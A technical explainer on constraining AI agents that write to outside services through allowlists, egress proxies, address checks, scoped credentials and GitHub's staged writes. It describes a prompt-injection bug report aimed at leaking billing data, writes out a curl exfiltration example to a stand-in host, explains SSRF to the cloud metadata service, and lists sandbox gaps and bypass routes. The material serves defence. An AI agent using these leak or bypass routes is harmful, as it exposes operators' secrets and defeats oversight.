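# Domain allowlists and concurrency limits for AI agents that write to external services

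## Agents that write to outside services

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop with a set of tools. The model reads material, requests an action, receives the result and repeats this until it finishes its task. Many tools only look things up. Others cause external side effects, which are changes that a tool call makes in a system outside the agent's own environment. For example, a tool call might open an issue in a bug tracker, post a comment or call a company's web API. If an agent ruins a file in its own working directory, its operator can throw the directory away. An issue in a public tracker is harder to take back because people may read, copy or act on it before anyone removes it.

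Operators use domain allowlists to restrict where an agent can write, and limits on parallel and total calls to restrict how much it can write before someone stops it.

A hypothetical company, Acme, keeps its code on GitHub, a service that hosts software projects in repositories. Acme runs an agent that reads the bug reports in the public repository acme/app and files an issue in a public tracker, acme/triage, for each real bug. Some bugs involve payments, so the agent can also read the private repository acme/billing. Anyone with a GitHub account can write a bug report in acme/app, and anyone can read acme/triage. The agent's job, as Acme designed it, therefore requires it to read text from strangers, have access to confidential code and publish to the world.

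### How an agent files an issue

A language model produces text, so it cannot contact GitHub by itself. To file an issue, it emits a tool call, a structured piece of text that names a tool and supplies the tool's inputs. The program that runs the model recognises the call and passes it on. In many agents the call goes to an MCP server, a program that offers tools to an agent through the Model Context Protocol (a common format for connecting models to outside systems) and often holds the credentials for the outside service. Under the Model Context Protocol documentation, tools are "model-controlled": the model can discover and invoke them automatically. A call from Acme's agent might look like this, without the protocol's housekeeping fields:

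```json
{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "create_issue",
    "arguments": {
      "repo": "acme/triage",
      "title": "Crash when a file name is empty",
      "body": "Steps to reproduce: ..."
    }
  }
}
```

The MCP server turns this into an ordinary web request. According to GitHub's *REST API endpoints for issues*, the request is a POST to the repository's list of issues. It carries the issue's title and text and an access token that must have write permission for issues. GitHub checks the token, stores the issue, sends out notifications and replies with the new issue's number and address. The MCP server returns that reply to the model as text.

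GitHub checks the token but has no access to the reasons behind the request, so a maintainer, a script and a hijacked agent that use the same token get the same result. If the request opens an issue, a maintainer can close it a minute later, but by then people have already received the notification emails.

In July 2026 the Model Context Protocol (2026) project announced a revision in which each request is self-contained, so any copy of a server can handle it without shared storage. An operator who runs several copies and wants to stop an agent after it opens five issues must therefore keep the count somewhere every copy can reach, because otherwise each copy could allow five.

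### Reads can also send data out

A read asks a service for information, and a write asks it to change something. On the web, a read is usually a GET request and a write is usually a POST. It is tempting to conclude that an agent with only read tools cannot affect anyone outside, but this is wrong. A GET request has an address, and the address can carry text chosen by whoever makes the request. Suppose Acme's agent fetches this page:

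`https://example.net/help?ref=billing-key-4471`

Whoever runs example.net now has the text after the equals sign. The request delivers the text even if the page doesn't exist and the server replies with an error. GitHub's endpoints for listing issues also accept text in the address, for example as a label filter, but that text goes to GitHub rather than to a stranger.

*How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes the permission system of Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code. File reads and text searches are among the tools that run without a further check, while web fetches go through one. Anthropic's test cases for data theft include credentials embedded in web addresses.

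The labels that MCP servers attach to their tools allow the same confusion. The `readOnlyHint` label indicates whether a tool modifies its environment, and `openWorldHint` indicates whether it interacts with outside entities. A tool that fetches web pages can correctly carry the read-only label and still transmit a secret. An operator therefore has to control which hosts an agent contacts as well as which posts it makes. Operators typically control the hosts with an egress proxy, a program that the agent's outgoing traffic must pass through.

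### How things go wrong

Acme's agent could cause harm if a stranger hijacks it, it makes a mistake, or it pursues its task further than anyone authorised.

Attackers hijack agents through prompt injection, which is text in material the agent reads that causes it to follow someone else's instructions. A bug report in acme/app might describe a plausible crash and then add that automated triage tools should include the payment settings from acme/billing so that developers can reproduce the fault. The model receives the report and Acme's instructions as one body of text and cannot reliably tell which parts it should obey. The UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) warns that prompt injection will remain a risk that no product can fully remove. It advises designers to plan for the worst an attacker could do with direct access to the system's tools. In Acme's case, the attacker would be able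 to read acme/billing and post in acme/triage.

Agents can make mistakes even when no attacker is involved. Anthropic describes agents that mistake a shared resource for a test copy, or another person's branch for their own. In one example, a user asked an agent to cancel "my job", and the agent picked the job with the closest matching name and tried to delete it. Acme's agent could similarly file an issue in the wrong repository. It could also report the same crash repeatedly if a bug keeps its search for existing issues from returning anything, because it may conclude each time that nobody has reported the crash.

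In the remaining case, the agent works on the right task but exceeds its authority. Anthropic calls this overeager behaviour and considers it hard to catch because the action looks like reasonable problem-solving. One agent hit an authentication error and began searching configuration files for other access tokens. Another wanted to share a script for debugging and prepared to upload it to GitHub Gist, a service for posting code snippets, although the user might have considered the script confidential. An overeager triage agent at Acme might find a spare token and use it to report a bug to the outside project that maintains a software library Acme uses.

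Anthropic also lists as a cause a misaligned model, meaning one that pursues a goal of its own, but wrote that it did not see this in practice at the time. Its defence against every cause is to block the action, which is useful because operators rarely know in advance why an agent will misbehave. For example, a rule that blocks posts outside acme/triage works equally well against an attacker and a misread repository name.

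### Blast radius

Blast radius is the most damage an agent can do before it is stopped, given what it can reach and how much it can write. It depends on three quantities:

- the number of places the agent can write to
- the number of writes it makes before someone or something stops it
- the harm that a single write can do.

A simple formula shows how they fit together. Let *R* be the set of places the agent can write to, *N* the number of writes it makes before it stops, and *h(r)* the worst harm that one write to place *r* can do. If the harm from separate writes adds up, then

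total harm ≤ *N* × (the largest *h(r)* for any *r* in *R*).

Allowlists shrink *R* and call limits cap *N*. As an invented example, suppose Acme's token can write to 40 repositories and the agent gets stuck in a loop, filing an issue every two seconds for eight hours. It files 14,400 issues across as many as 40 repositories. If a maintainer needs five minutes to read and close each one, cleaning up takes 1,200 hours. (GitHub may slow down an account that posts this quickly, so the real figure would probably be lower.) With an allowlist that contains only acme/triage and a quota of five issues per run, the same fault produces five issues in one tracker, which take 25 minutes to clean up.

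If one of those five issues contains a working payment key from acme/billing, the damage could be far greater than a night of spam, even though the agent stayed in the approved tracker and within its quota. Neither the allowlist nor the quota directly limits the harm of a single write. An allowlist can reduce that harm indirectly by excluding the places where a bad post would hurt most, but acme/triage is public and must stay on the list for the agent to do its work.

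The formula is also cruder than it looks, because the total harm is not always the sum of the individual harms. A second copy of a leaked key does little extra damage, but thousands of junk issues can bury a report of a serious security hole, which is worse than the minutes spent closing them. The formula still helps an operator see what each control contributes. For example, a tighter call limit works well against spam but poorly against leaks.

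### Why the limit has to sit outside the model

It is worth stating in the agent's instructions that it must file at most five issues, and only in acme/triage. The model will probably comply most of the time, but the instructions don't enforce the limit. The model receives them as text alongside the bug reports, and its output depends on all of that text, so a persuasive bug report or a misreading can still lead to a sixth call.

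A program outside the model can enforce the limit instead. Before it forwards a `create_issue` call, it checks that the repository is on its list and that fewer than five issues have been filed. If either check fails, it returns an error and GitHub receives nothing. The checks do not depend on the bug report or the model's reasons, so the limits hold whatever the model outputs. The NCSC recommends deterministic safeguards like this one, which constrain the system's actions without relying on a language model, over merely trying to keep malicious text away from the model.

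Anyone can write a Model Context Protocol (MCP) server, and a dishonest server can label a tool as read-only and then delete the user's files. When the labels were first proposed, Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, wondered how a client could use information it could not trust. The maintainers decided to call every label a hint and require clients to distrust hints from untrusted servers. In its March post on tool annotations, the project (Model Context Protocol, 2026) assigns hard guarantees, such as preventing a tool from leaking data, to network controls or sandboxing. It still sees a role for hints in decisions such as when to ask a user for confirmation.

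### GitHub's threat model

GitHub has built a product around enforcement outside the model. GitHub Agentic Workflows runs AI agents, often with no person watching, inside GitHub Actions, its service for automating work on repositories. GitHub's *Under the hood*, published in March 2026, sets out the threat model, a statement of what an attacker or a faulty component might do. GitHub assumes that an agent will try to read and write things it should not, communicate over unintended channels and "abuse legitimate channels to perform unwanted actions".

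The assumption about legitimate channels matters most for Acme. A firewall can stop the agent from contacting example.net, but the agent's job is to file issues in acme/triage, so that channel has to stay open. GitHub's example is an agent that has no secrets but still floods a repository with pointless issues or fills its posts with objectionable links. An agent that finds a secret could encode it in a public issue or comment.

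To avoid these problems, GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026) uses staged writes, in which the agent only requests a write, and a separate program with its own credentials checks the request and carries it out later. The specification rejects forbidding writes altogether because that would limit agents to giving advice. It also rejects manual approval of every action, which creates bottlenecks, and broad permissions, which accept too much risk for the sake of convenience.

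The separation of credentials is what makes the check hard to avoid. By default, everything in a GitHub Actions job shares one zone of trust, and an agent that can run shell commands can search configuration files and logs for tokens. If it found one with write permission, it could call GitHub's API directly and bypass any program that counts its calls. The specification therefore requires the following to hold at every moment *t* while the agent runs:

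permissions(agent, *t*) ∩ {issues: write, pull-requests: write, …} = ∅

The symbol ∩ means the elements two sets have in common, and ∅ is the empty set. The formula means that the agent never has permission to write to GitHub, so even an attacker who fully controls it can only submit requests for the separate program to check.

This protection depends on the systems around the agent. GitHub's *Security Architecture* says its guarantees may fail if the firewall, the gateway that runs the MCP servers, or the operating system's kernel has a flaw. It also lists misconfiguration and overly permissive settings as sources of violations. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) reports one such failure, in which a model instructed to post its results only to Slack got past a sandbox and published them on GitHub. Other people used the results even though OpenAI quickly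 closed the post.

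## Restricting which hosts an agent can reach

A domain allowlist names the hosts an agent may connect to, and an egress proxy refuses connections to all others. A host name is the part of a web address that identifies a service, such as `api.github.com`. Acme's agent only needs to reach `api.github.com`, where it reads bug reports and files issues, and its model provider.

Allowlists also save people time. Claude Code asks the user before it runs most commands, and Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) warns that people who constantly click "approve" may stop paying attention to what they are approving. Anthropic therefore added a sandbox, a restricted environment where commands can run without a prompt because they can only touch approved files and hosts. In Anthropic's internal use, the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%, though this figure does not measure how many attacks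 it stopped.

### One connection, step by step

Suppose a malicious bug report persuades Acme's agent to run this command, which uses the program curl to fetch a web page:

`curl "https://example.net/help?ref=billing-key-4471"`

In Claude Code's sandbox, as Anthropic documents it, the following happens:

1. The command starts without a direct route to the network. On Linux it runs in a separate network namespace, which is a private set of network connections that the operating system provides, and this one has no link to the outside. On macOS the built-in Seatbelt framework blocks connections other than the one to the proxy.
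2. Settings such as `HTTPS_PROXY` tell curl where to find the proxy, which runs outside the sandbox. Curl sends it a short request, `CONNECT example.net:443`. (Port 443 is the usual port for encrypted web traffic.)
3. The proxy reads the host name and compares it with the lists of allowed and denied domains.
4. The name isn't on the allowed list, so the proxy refuses, or waits while someone decides whether to approve the host. If the answer is no, example.net receives nothing, including the text after the equals sign.

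If the command had requested `api.github.com` instead, the proxy would have looked up its IP address, connected to it and passed data in both directions. Curl would then have set up an encrypted session with GitHub through the proxy.

The missing route in the first step stops programs from bypassing the allowlist. Settings such as `HTTPS_PROXY` can't do this alone, because a program can ignore them. Plain ssh and most database drivers do, so inside the sandbox they can't connect even to an approved host. This is a nuisance for developers, but it is safer than setting the variables and leaving the network open, which would let any program that ignored them reach any host.

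Docker runs each agent in a virtual machine. Under Docker's *Local policy*, every outbound TCP connection (the kind that web traffic and ssh normally use) passes through a filtering proxy on the user's computer. The agent has administrator rights inside the virtual machine, according to Docker's *Default security posture*, but it can't use them to turn off the filter because the proxy runs outside the virtual machine. In GitHub Agentic Workflows, a trusted firewall container sets the network rules with the Linux tool iptables, then launches the agent in a separate container.

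### Matching host names

An exact entry matches one host name, and a wildcard entry uses an asterisk to match several. Under the usual convention, `*.github.io` matches `user.github.io` but not `github.io` itself, because the pattern requires something before the dot. Docker's *Policy concepts* follows this convention and also limits a single asterisk to one subdomain level, so matching `docs.user.github.io` requires `**.github.io`.

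GitHub Agentic Workflows uses the same symbols differently. According to GitHub's *Network Permissions*, a plain entry also covers every subdomain, and a wildcard entry also covers the base domain. The results for three hosts are:

| Requested host | Docker, `github.io` | Docker, `*.github.io` | GitHub Agentic Workflows, either entry |
|---|---|---|---|
| `github.io` | allowed | refused | allowed |
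| `user.github.io` | refused | allowed | allowed |
| `docs.user.github.io` | refused | refused | allowed |

An operator who copies a list from Docker to GitHub Agentic Workflows therefore grants more access than the original list did. GitHub's documentation also lists `raw.githubusercontent.com` as covered by a `github.com` entry, although it is not a subdomain of github.com, so anyone who depends on that should test it.

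A program that matches the wildcard `*.github.io` must check that the hostname ends in `.github.io`, including the leading dot. If it checked only for `github.io`, it would also accept `notgithub.io`, which a stranger could register.

A wildcard also works best when one organisation controls every name it covers. GitHub lets its users publish their own websites under github.io, so `*.github.io` lets an agent read pages that strangers wrote. Balanced, Docker's ready-made list for developers, included `*.blob.core.windows.net` in version 0.35.0, according to an earlier edition of Docker's *Local policy*. That wildcard covers Microsoft's Azure file storage, where any customer can create a name, so it allows an agent to reach a stranger's storage and is a possible route for leaks.

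Some allowlist entries specify a protocol or port as well as a hostname. In GitHub Agentic Workflows, `https://api.github.com` permits only encrypted connections, an entry that starts with `http://` permits only unencrypted ones, and an entry without a prefix permits both. GitHub supports these prefixes only when Copilot, its own AI system, runs the workflow. Acme should choose the encrypted form, because an unencrypted request would expose Acme's access token to anyone who can watch the network. A workflow with an unsupported prefix, such as `ftp://`, fails to compile, according to GitHub's *Network Configuration Guide*. Docker lets users name a port, as in `example.com:443`. Claude Code does too, but an entry without a port allows every port on that host.

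Lists can also contradict each other. If an allow entry and a deny entry both match a host, the deny entry wins in Claude Code, GitHub Agentic Workflows and Docker's current sandboxes. An earlier Docker Desktop sandbox, now deprecated, gave priority to the most specific entry. According to that sandbox's *Network policies*, a user could block `*.example.com` and still allow `api.example.com`. Under Docker's current rules, the same entries block `api.example.com`.

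### Names, addresses and redirects

The allowlist contains names, but computers connect to numerical addresses. The Domain Name System (DNS) translates names into addresses, and whoever controls a name chooses its address. Suppose Acme allows `*.example.org` and a stranger controls one name under it. The stranger can point that name at `127.0.0.1`, the address a computer uses for itself, or at a machine on Acme's internal network, and the name will still pass the allowlist.

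This is dangerous because the proxy runs outside the sandbox and can often reach services that the agent can't. It allows server-side request forgery, an attack in which someone makes a server send a request that they could not send directly. A particularly valuable target is `169.254.169.254`, the address of the metadata service on many cloud machines. Programs on the machine use this service to learn about their environment, and it can give them temporary credentials for the owner's cloud account. If the proxy forwarded a request there, Acme's agent could receive those credentials and post them in acme/triage.

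Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, studied this kind of attack with TicketOracle, a web application they built around a language model that can call tools. They tried to manipulate the model into sending requests from the application's server, using five attack scenarios and seven models. Susceptibility varied substantially between models, but the researchers attribute the flaw to the application, which did not restrict the requests the model could trigger. They constructed the scenario by analogy with documented attacks, so their results show that the attack can work but not how often it happens in deployed systems. For Acme, a more resistant model would make an attack less likely to succeed, but blocking the metadata address would stop the request whichever model Acme used.

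A proxy therefore needs a second check after the first. Let *A* be the allowed names, *D* the denied names and *L* the blocked addresses. For a requested host *h*, the proxy should connect only if

*h* ∈ *A*, *h* ∉ *D* and address(*h*) ∉ *L*.

The symbol ∈ means "matches an entry in" and ∉ means "matches no entry in". The proxy should also connect to the address it checked rather than look the name up again, because the domain's owner may have changed the address in the meantime.

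Claude Code's proxy refuses a connection to an allowed name if the name resolves only to local addresses, which include `127.0.0.1`, the metadata address and any address that belongs to the user's own machine. Before version 2.1.284, the proxy connected to whatever address an allowed name resolved to.

The check does not block an allowed intranet name that resolves to a private address, such as one beginning with 10. This lets an agent reach an internal package server, but the operator has to trust whoever controls the names on the list. The proxy also skips the check when it sends traffic through a company's upstream proxy, because the upstream proxy performs the lookup. The upstream proxy then needs its own block on local addresses.

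Docker's earlier Desktop sandbox blocked a wider set of addresses by default, including all the common private ranges, but it skipped the address check for any host the user had allowed. Docker said this was for performance. The check caught an unlisted alias for the user's own machine, but an allowed hostname could still resolve to a blocked address.

#### Name lookups

A DNS lookup is an outgoing message, and the name in it can carry text just as a web address can. A sandbox that blocked web connections but let programs look up any name could still leak some information. Claude Code's proxy looks up a name only after the name passes the allowlist. In Docker's sandboxes, an internal resolver performs lookups and enforces the network policy.

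#### Redirects

A web server can answer a request with a redirect to a different address, so an approved site could redirect Acme's agent to example.net. If the agent's traffic goes through an egress proxy, the program has to open a new connection for the new host, and the proxy checks that name too. The risk is greater with a tool that does its own checking. If it checks only the first address against its list, an approved site can redirect it anywhere, including to the metadata service.

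Redirects also cause confusing failures. A download may start on an approved site and then redirect to a storage host that isn't on the allowlist. The fix is to identify the host the download needs and add only that host, rather than a broad wildcard.

### What the proxy can see

Most web traffic is encrypted with TLS. A proxy that doesn't decrypt it can see the host name and port the program asked for, the address it connected to, the time of the connection and roughly how much data went each way. It can't see the path, the type of request, the access token or the text.

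Compare two requests that Acme's agent might make:

- `GET https://api.github.com/repos/acme/billing/contents/settings.json`
- `POST https://api.github.com/repos/acme/triage/issues`

An agent can send one GitHub API request to read a confidential file and another to publish an issue. A proxy that doesn't decrypt traffic can't distinguish between them because both are connections to `api.github.com` on port 443, so it has to allow or refuse both. For the same reason, it can't limit the agent to one repository.

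To inspect the contents of a request, the proxy has to decrypt the connection, then encrypt it again before sending the request on. Programs in the sandbox must trust a certificate that belongs to the proxy, because otherwise they would reject the intercepted connection as a possible attack. The proxy handles access tokens and private text in readable form, so a flaw in it can expose them. Some programs accept only a specific certificate from their server, so they won't connect through such a proxy.

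GitHub's *Agentic Workflow Firewall* can filter requests by URL path, but an operator has to turn on this inspection because it is off by default. One of GitHub's sample rules is `https://api.github.com/repos/*/issues`. Acme should not copy it unchanged, because the asterisk allows access to issues in other repositories as well as acme/triage.

Docker lets users write rules for a type of request and a path, for example to permit reads from an API but not writes. If such a rule applies to a host and the proxy can't inspect a connection, the proxy blocks it, which is safer than letting it through. But a rule that allows only reads doesn't always prevent writes, because Docker's local policy permits a request if any rule allows it and no rule denies it. If the Balanced list already allows a host and a user adds a rule that allows only reads from it, writes still go through until the user explicitly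 denies them or removes the broader permission.

Claude Code's built-in proxy doesn't decrypt traffic by default, but an experimental setting makes it do so in order to keep credentials away from the agent. Commands in the sandbox get a placeholder, and the proxy replaces it with the real token in requests to approved hosts. Docker's proxy similarly adds credentials to outgoing requests, and the agent can't read them. A hijacked agent could still use the token on the approved service, but it couldn't copy it into a public issue.

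With Claude Code, the operator should also specify which hosts may receive each token. Otherwise the proxy replaces the placeholder with the real token in requests to every host on the allowlist. If Acme approved both `api.github.com` and a package registry, a command could send the placeholder to the registry, and the proxy would deliver the real GitHub token there.

Anthropic and Docker both document another limitation, domain fronting, in which a request shows the proxy an approved host name but goes to a different site. A proxy that doesn't inspect the encrypted traffic relies on the name the program supplied, so it may not detect the mismatch. For operators who need a stronger guarantee, Anthropic recommends a custom proxy that decrypts and inspects traffic. That proxy then has to do all the filtering, because Claude Code's domain lists and local-address check no longer apply to that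 traffic.

### How four products compare

The table shows how each product behaves, according to its current documentation. GitHub's Copilot agent works on code in the cloud and proposes changes. Its firewall is a separate product from the one in GitHub Agentic Workflows.

| Product | What the network control covers | Default | What happens to an unlisted host |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code sandbox | Shell commands and the processes they start | Off; once the user turns it on, the list starts empty | Depends on the permission mode; the user may get a prompt |
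| GitHub Copilot agent firewall | Processes the agent starts through its Bash tool | On, with a recommended list | The firewall blocks it and Copilot posts a warning |
| GitHub Agentic Workflows | The agent's execution inside the firewall | On, with basic infrastructure hosts | The firewall blocks and logs it |
| Docker Sandboxes, on the user's computer | All outbound TCP traffic from the sandbox | The user chooses Open, Balanced or Locked Down | Open allows it; the other two block it and ask for approval |

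The defaults reflect what each vendor expects an agent to do. Copilot's recommended list includes package registries for common programming languages, because a coding agent has to install software. Acme's triage agent doesn't install anything, so it could work without those hosts. By default, repository administrators can add entries to Copilot's list, though organisation owners can forbid this.

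When the firewall blocks a request, GitHub adds a warning to the pull request, the page where people review a proposed change. The warning shows the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it. This helps a reviewer notice an attack, but if the repository is public and the command contains a key, the warning could publish the key. Operators should check how GitHub handles keys in these warnings before relying on them.

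Docker's strictest setting, Locked Down, starts with no approved hosts. Agents still need to contact their models, so Docker's kits, which are packages of settings for particular agents, can add the hosts those agents need, even under Locked Down. A user who wants to know what an agent can reach therefore has to inspect the combined rules.

#### Tools outside the boundary

The most important gap for Acme is MCP servers, because its agent files issues through one. Copilot's firewall doesn't apply to MCP servers or to the steps that set up the agent's environment. Claude Code's sandbox doesn't cover local MCP servers either, and they run with the user's full access.

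In both products, the agent could still file issues even if the operator removed `api.github.com` from the list. The problem is more serious if an MCP server can fetch arbitrary web pages. The proxy would block the curl command to example.net, but the agent could fetch the same address through the MCP server, and the sandbox would not stop it. Claude Code's own tool for fetching web pages, WebFetch, also runs outside the sandbox and follows separate permission rules.

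An operator can close this gap by running the whole agent, including its MCP servers, inside one boundary. Anthropic suggests a container, a virtual machine or the sandbox runtime, the open-source package that Claude Code's sandbox is built on. The allowlist must then include the model provider, because the program that contacts the model is also inside the boundary. An MCP server that runs on another company's computers stays outside, and the proxy can only control whether the agent reaches it.

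Docker's network policy covers connections from the sandbox. Organisations can write a separate policy for the tools that agents use through Docker's MCP gateway, and this policy blocks anything it doesn't explicitly permit. Without an organisation policy, developers can register any MCP server.

#### Ways the sandbox can be absent

Claude Code's sandbox is off until someone turns it on. If it then can't start, perhaps because a required package is missing, Claude Code runs commands without it by default. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, an earlier version of the documentation, says that the user sees a warning when this happens. The warning is little help to Acme, because its agent works at night with nobody watching.

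Claude can also retry a command outside the sandbox after it fails inside. Depending on the permission settings, the retry may need approval, but an existing rule that approves all curl commands also approves an unsandboxed curl command. Acme can rule out both cases with these settings:

```json
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false
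  }
}
```

The second setting makes Claude Code exit if the sandbox can't start, and the third prevents it from retrying commands outside the sandbox. Acme also needs `strictAllowlist`, which refuses unlisted hosts without asking anyone. This matters most in the mode that skips permission prompts, which operators may choose for unattended agents, because Claude Code then allows unlisted hosts unless `strictAllowlist` or an equivalent administrator setting is on.

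Exceptions to the sandbox can undo these precautions. On macOS, some command-line tools fail to verify encrypted connections inside the sandbox, including `gh`, GitHub's tool for tasks such as opening issues. Anthropic's troubleshooting advice includes running such tools outside the sandbox, where they have the user's full access and stored credentials. If Acme followed this advice for `gh`, the program best suited to posting on GitHub, it would be exempt from the network limits.

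GitHub Agentic Workflows has an older setting that disables its firewall. With the firewall off, the domain list still removes links to unapproved sites from text the workflow processes, but it no longer stops the agent from contacting those sites. An operator who reads only the domain list could easily miss the difference.

### When the list is empty

If Acme's agent only contacts GitHub through an MCP server outside the sandbox, its shell commands don't need the network at all. The safest allowlist for those commands is an empty one. Unfortunately, an empty list is ambiguous: it can mean that the operator approves no hosts or that the operator never set a restriction. A programmer can confuse the two by accident, as in this invented example in Python:

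```python
if allowed_domains:
    block_everything_except(allowed_domains)
```

The program blocks every host that isn't on the allowlist, as long as the list contains at least one domain. Python treats an empty list as false, so if the allowlist is empty, the program skips the restriction and lets the agent reach any host, when it should block them all.

Anthropic's sandbox runtime had a flaw with this effect. GitLab's *Anthropic Sandbox Runtime Incorrectly Implemented Network Sandboxing* reports that the runtime did not properly enforce its network sandbox if the policy listed no allowed domains, so code inside the sandbox could make requests to the outside. Anthropic fixed the flaw, CVE-2025-66479, in version 0.0.16. GitLab attributes it to a bug in the sandboxing logic, which may have differed from the example above.

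The failure appeared only when the list was empty, a case many people would assume is too simple to test. With one approved domain, the sandbox would have correctly allowed that domain and refused the others, so a tester who tried only ordinary lists would have missed the failure.

An empty list can also open the network by design. In Docker's cloud service for agents, which is separate from the sandboxes on a user's own computer, a sandbox with an empty combined allowlist used to be able to reach any destination that no deny rule blocked, according to an earlier version of Docker's *Network policies*. According to the newer version, an empty list blocks everything by default, but accounts that predate the change keep the open setting. In GitHub Agentic Workflows, `network: {}` denies all access, while leaving out the `network` setting allows a default list of infrastructure hosts.

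Acme should therefore test the boundary by trying to cross it. These tests need no real secrets:

| Setup | Attempt | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| Empty allowlist | Fetch a page from `example.com` | Refused |
| Only `api.github.com` allowed | Fetch a public page from `api.github.com` | Connects |
| Only `api.github.com` allowed | Fetch a page from `example.com` | Refused |
| Only `api.github.com` allowed | Connect to it with a program that ignores the proxy settings | Fails |
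| A test name allowed that resolves to `127.0.0.1` | Connect to that name | Refused |
| MCP servers placed inside the boundary | Ask an MCP tool to fetch an unlisted page | Refused |

The second test is needed because a sandbox with a broken network connection would pass all the others. Acme should repeat the tests after each software update and each change to the list.

The test also has to run where the agent's commands run. In Claude Code, a command that the user types at the shell prompt usually runs outside the sandbox, so it can succeed even when the sandbox is working. Anthropic advises users to ask Claude to run the test instead. Docker's `sbx policy check network` command reports whether the current policy would allow a given host. It can catch a mistaken wildcard before the agent starts, but only a real connection attempt from inside the sandbox can reveal a proxy that fails to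 enforce the policy.

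## Restricting what an agent can write on an approved service

Acme's proxy has to allow `api.github.com`, but that host name serves every repository on GitHub, and a proxy that doesn't decrypt traffic can't distinguish requests to different repositories. Acme needs narrower controls based on the repository, the kind of write and the text being written.

### Scoping the credential

An access token limits every program that holds it. In the earlier example, Acme's token could write to 40 repositories. If it lets its holder open, edit, close and comment on issues, it permits 40 × 4 = 160 combinations of repository and operation. Restricting the token to acme/triage would reduce that number to four.

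A GitHub token alone can't limit an agent to opening issues, because the `issues: write` permission also lets it rewrite or close other people's. To allow one without the other, a program has to check each request against two lists. The target allowlist contains the repositories, projects or channels the agent may write to, and the operation allowlist contains the kinds of write it may make.

Let *C* be the combinations that the credential permits, *T* the target allowlist and *O* the operation allowlist. The agent can make only the writes in

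*C* ∩ (*T* × *O*),

where *T* × *O* means every pairing of a target in *T* with an operation in *O*. For Acme, *T* contains only acme/triage and *O* contains only the creation of issues, so one combination remains.

It remains with either token, as long as the program works. If a bug made the program skip the target check, the agent could open issues in all 40 repositories with the broad token, but only in acme/triage with the narrow one. Acme should therefore narrow the token as well as write the lists.

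GitHub's *Using at Scale in Organizations* recommends GitHub Apps over personal access tokens for work across repositories. A GitHub App gives software its own identity and short-lived tokens, whereas a personal access token acts for a human user. In GitHub Agentic Workflows, an operator can list the repositories that an App's token covers. The entry `["*"]` extends the token to every repository where the organisation installed the App. An operator can also use a separate App for each kind of write, so that the token for posting comments can't start other workflows.

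### Targets, operations and fixed fields

GitHub Agentic Workflows calls the writes an agent may request "safe outputs". Acme could configure them like this:

```yaml
safe-outputs:
  allowed-domains: [docs.acme.example]
  report-failure-as-issue: false
  github-app:
    client-id: ${{ vars.TRIAGE_APP_ID }}
    private-key: ${{ secrets.TRIAGE_APP_KEY }}
    repositories: [triage]
  create-issue:
    target-repo: "acme/triage"
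    allowed-repos: ["acme/triage"]
    title-prefix: "[agent] "
    labels: [needs-review]
    max: 5
```

Entries such as `create-issue` make up the operation allowlist. GitHub's *Safe Outputs* lists separate entries for closing an issue, adding a label and merging a pull request. The agent gets a tool only for the entries the operator includes, apart from a few reporting tools that are on by default. Some entries allow finer choices. An operator who lets an agent update issues must separately enable changes to the title, the text and the status, and one who lets it review code can permit comments but not approvals. An organisation can also turn off pull requests for all its workflows with a single variable. The safe-outputs server then does not start for any workflow that GitHub finds is configured to open them.

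Operators should consider what an operation triggers as well as what it changes. In many projects, adding a label that starts with `~` triggers a workflow. Assigning an issue to Copilot starts another agent, with its own permissions.

If a workflow omits the `safe-outputs` section entirely, GitHub still lets the agent create one issue per run, with a label and title prefix taken from the workflow's name. To prevent this, an operator has to set `create-issue: false`. GitHub also opens an issue when a run fails, by default in the repository where the workflow runs. For Acme this would be acme/app, which the public reads, so the configuration turns these reports off and Acme has to watch for failures some other way.

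A target can be narrower than a repository. By default, the agent can comment only on the issue or pull request that started the run. The operator can instead set the target to a particular issue or pull request number, or to `"*"`, which lets the agent choose. If Acme later allowed comments, the default would limit each run's comments to the bug report that started it.

The configuration also makes the write job add "[agent]" to the start of every issue title and attach the label `needs-review`, whatever the model wrote. This doesn't prevent bad issues, but it lets maintainers recognise the agent's issues and find them all if they need to clean up.

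Fixed fields can also protect other people's issues, because an operator can let the agent close only issues with a certain label or title prefix. This protection fails if the agent can attach the label itself. Suppose Acme let its agent add any label and close any issue labelled `automated`. A hijacked agent could put `automated` on a customer's bug report and then close it. To prevent this, Acme would have to block `automated` in the settings for adding labels.

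#### Trackers outside GitHub

GitHub Agentic Workflows can also write to Jira, Linear and Azure DevOps, three other services for tracking work. The documented controls on targets differ:

| Service | Who chooses where a new item goes | Limit on later changes |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub | The operator, or the agent from a list | Repository, item, label or title prefix |
| Linear | The operator fixes the team and can fix the project | A fixed issue |
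| Azure DevOps | The operator can fix the area of the project | Named items, or items within an area |
| Jira | The agent supplies the project | None listed |

GitHub lists only two settings for each Jira operation, a count limit and a preview mode. An operator who wants to keep the agent in one Jira project therefore has to restrict the Jira account. An operator who switched from Linear to Jira and gave the agent an equally broad account would lose the limit on where it can write, even without removing a line that looked like such a limit.

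### From request to issue

In GitHub's system of staged writes, the agent's `create_issue` call goes to an MCP server that has no access to GitHub's API. The server adds the request as one line in a file. After the agent's job ends, a separate job with write permission downloads the file and processes it.

GitHub sets out the process in version 1.29.8 of its specification, a working draft dated 1 October 2026. The draft treats the file as something the agent controls, so the decisive checks have to happen after the file leaves the agent's job. They run in this order:

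1. **Schema.** The request must have the right structure. An issue needs a title and a text, and the draft's schema accepts no fields beyond those it lists. A badly formed request gets error E001.
2. **Count.** The job compares the number of requests of each kind with the limit for that kind. Too many produce E002.
3. **Sanitising.** The job removes or disarms text that could cause harm when GitHub displays or processes it. If it can't make the text safe, it returns E008.
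4. **Link domains.** The job replaces links to unapproved sites and lets the request continue.
5. **Target repository.** The repository must be one the operator allows. Otherwise the job returns E004.
6. **References.** A request can refer to an issue that doesn't exist yet, for example to a parent issue from the same run. The job replaces the temporary name with the real issue number, or returns E005 if it can't find one.
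7. **API call.** The job sends the request to GitHub. If GitHub refuses it, perhaps because the token lacks permission, the job returns E007.

If a request fails any of the first six stages, the job must not send it to GitHub. One failure doesn't stop the other requests in the file, except that exceeding the count limit causes all requests of the same kind to be rejected.
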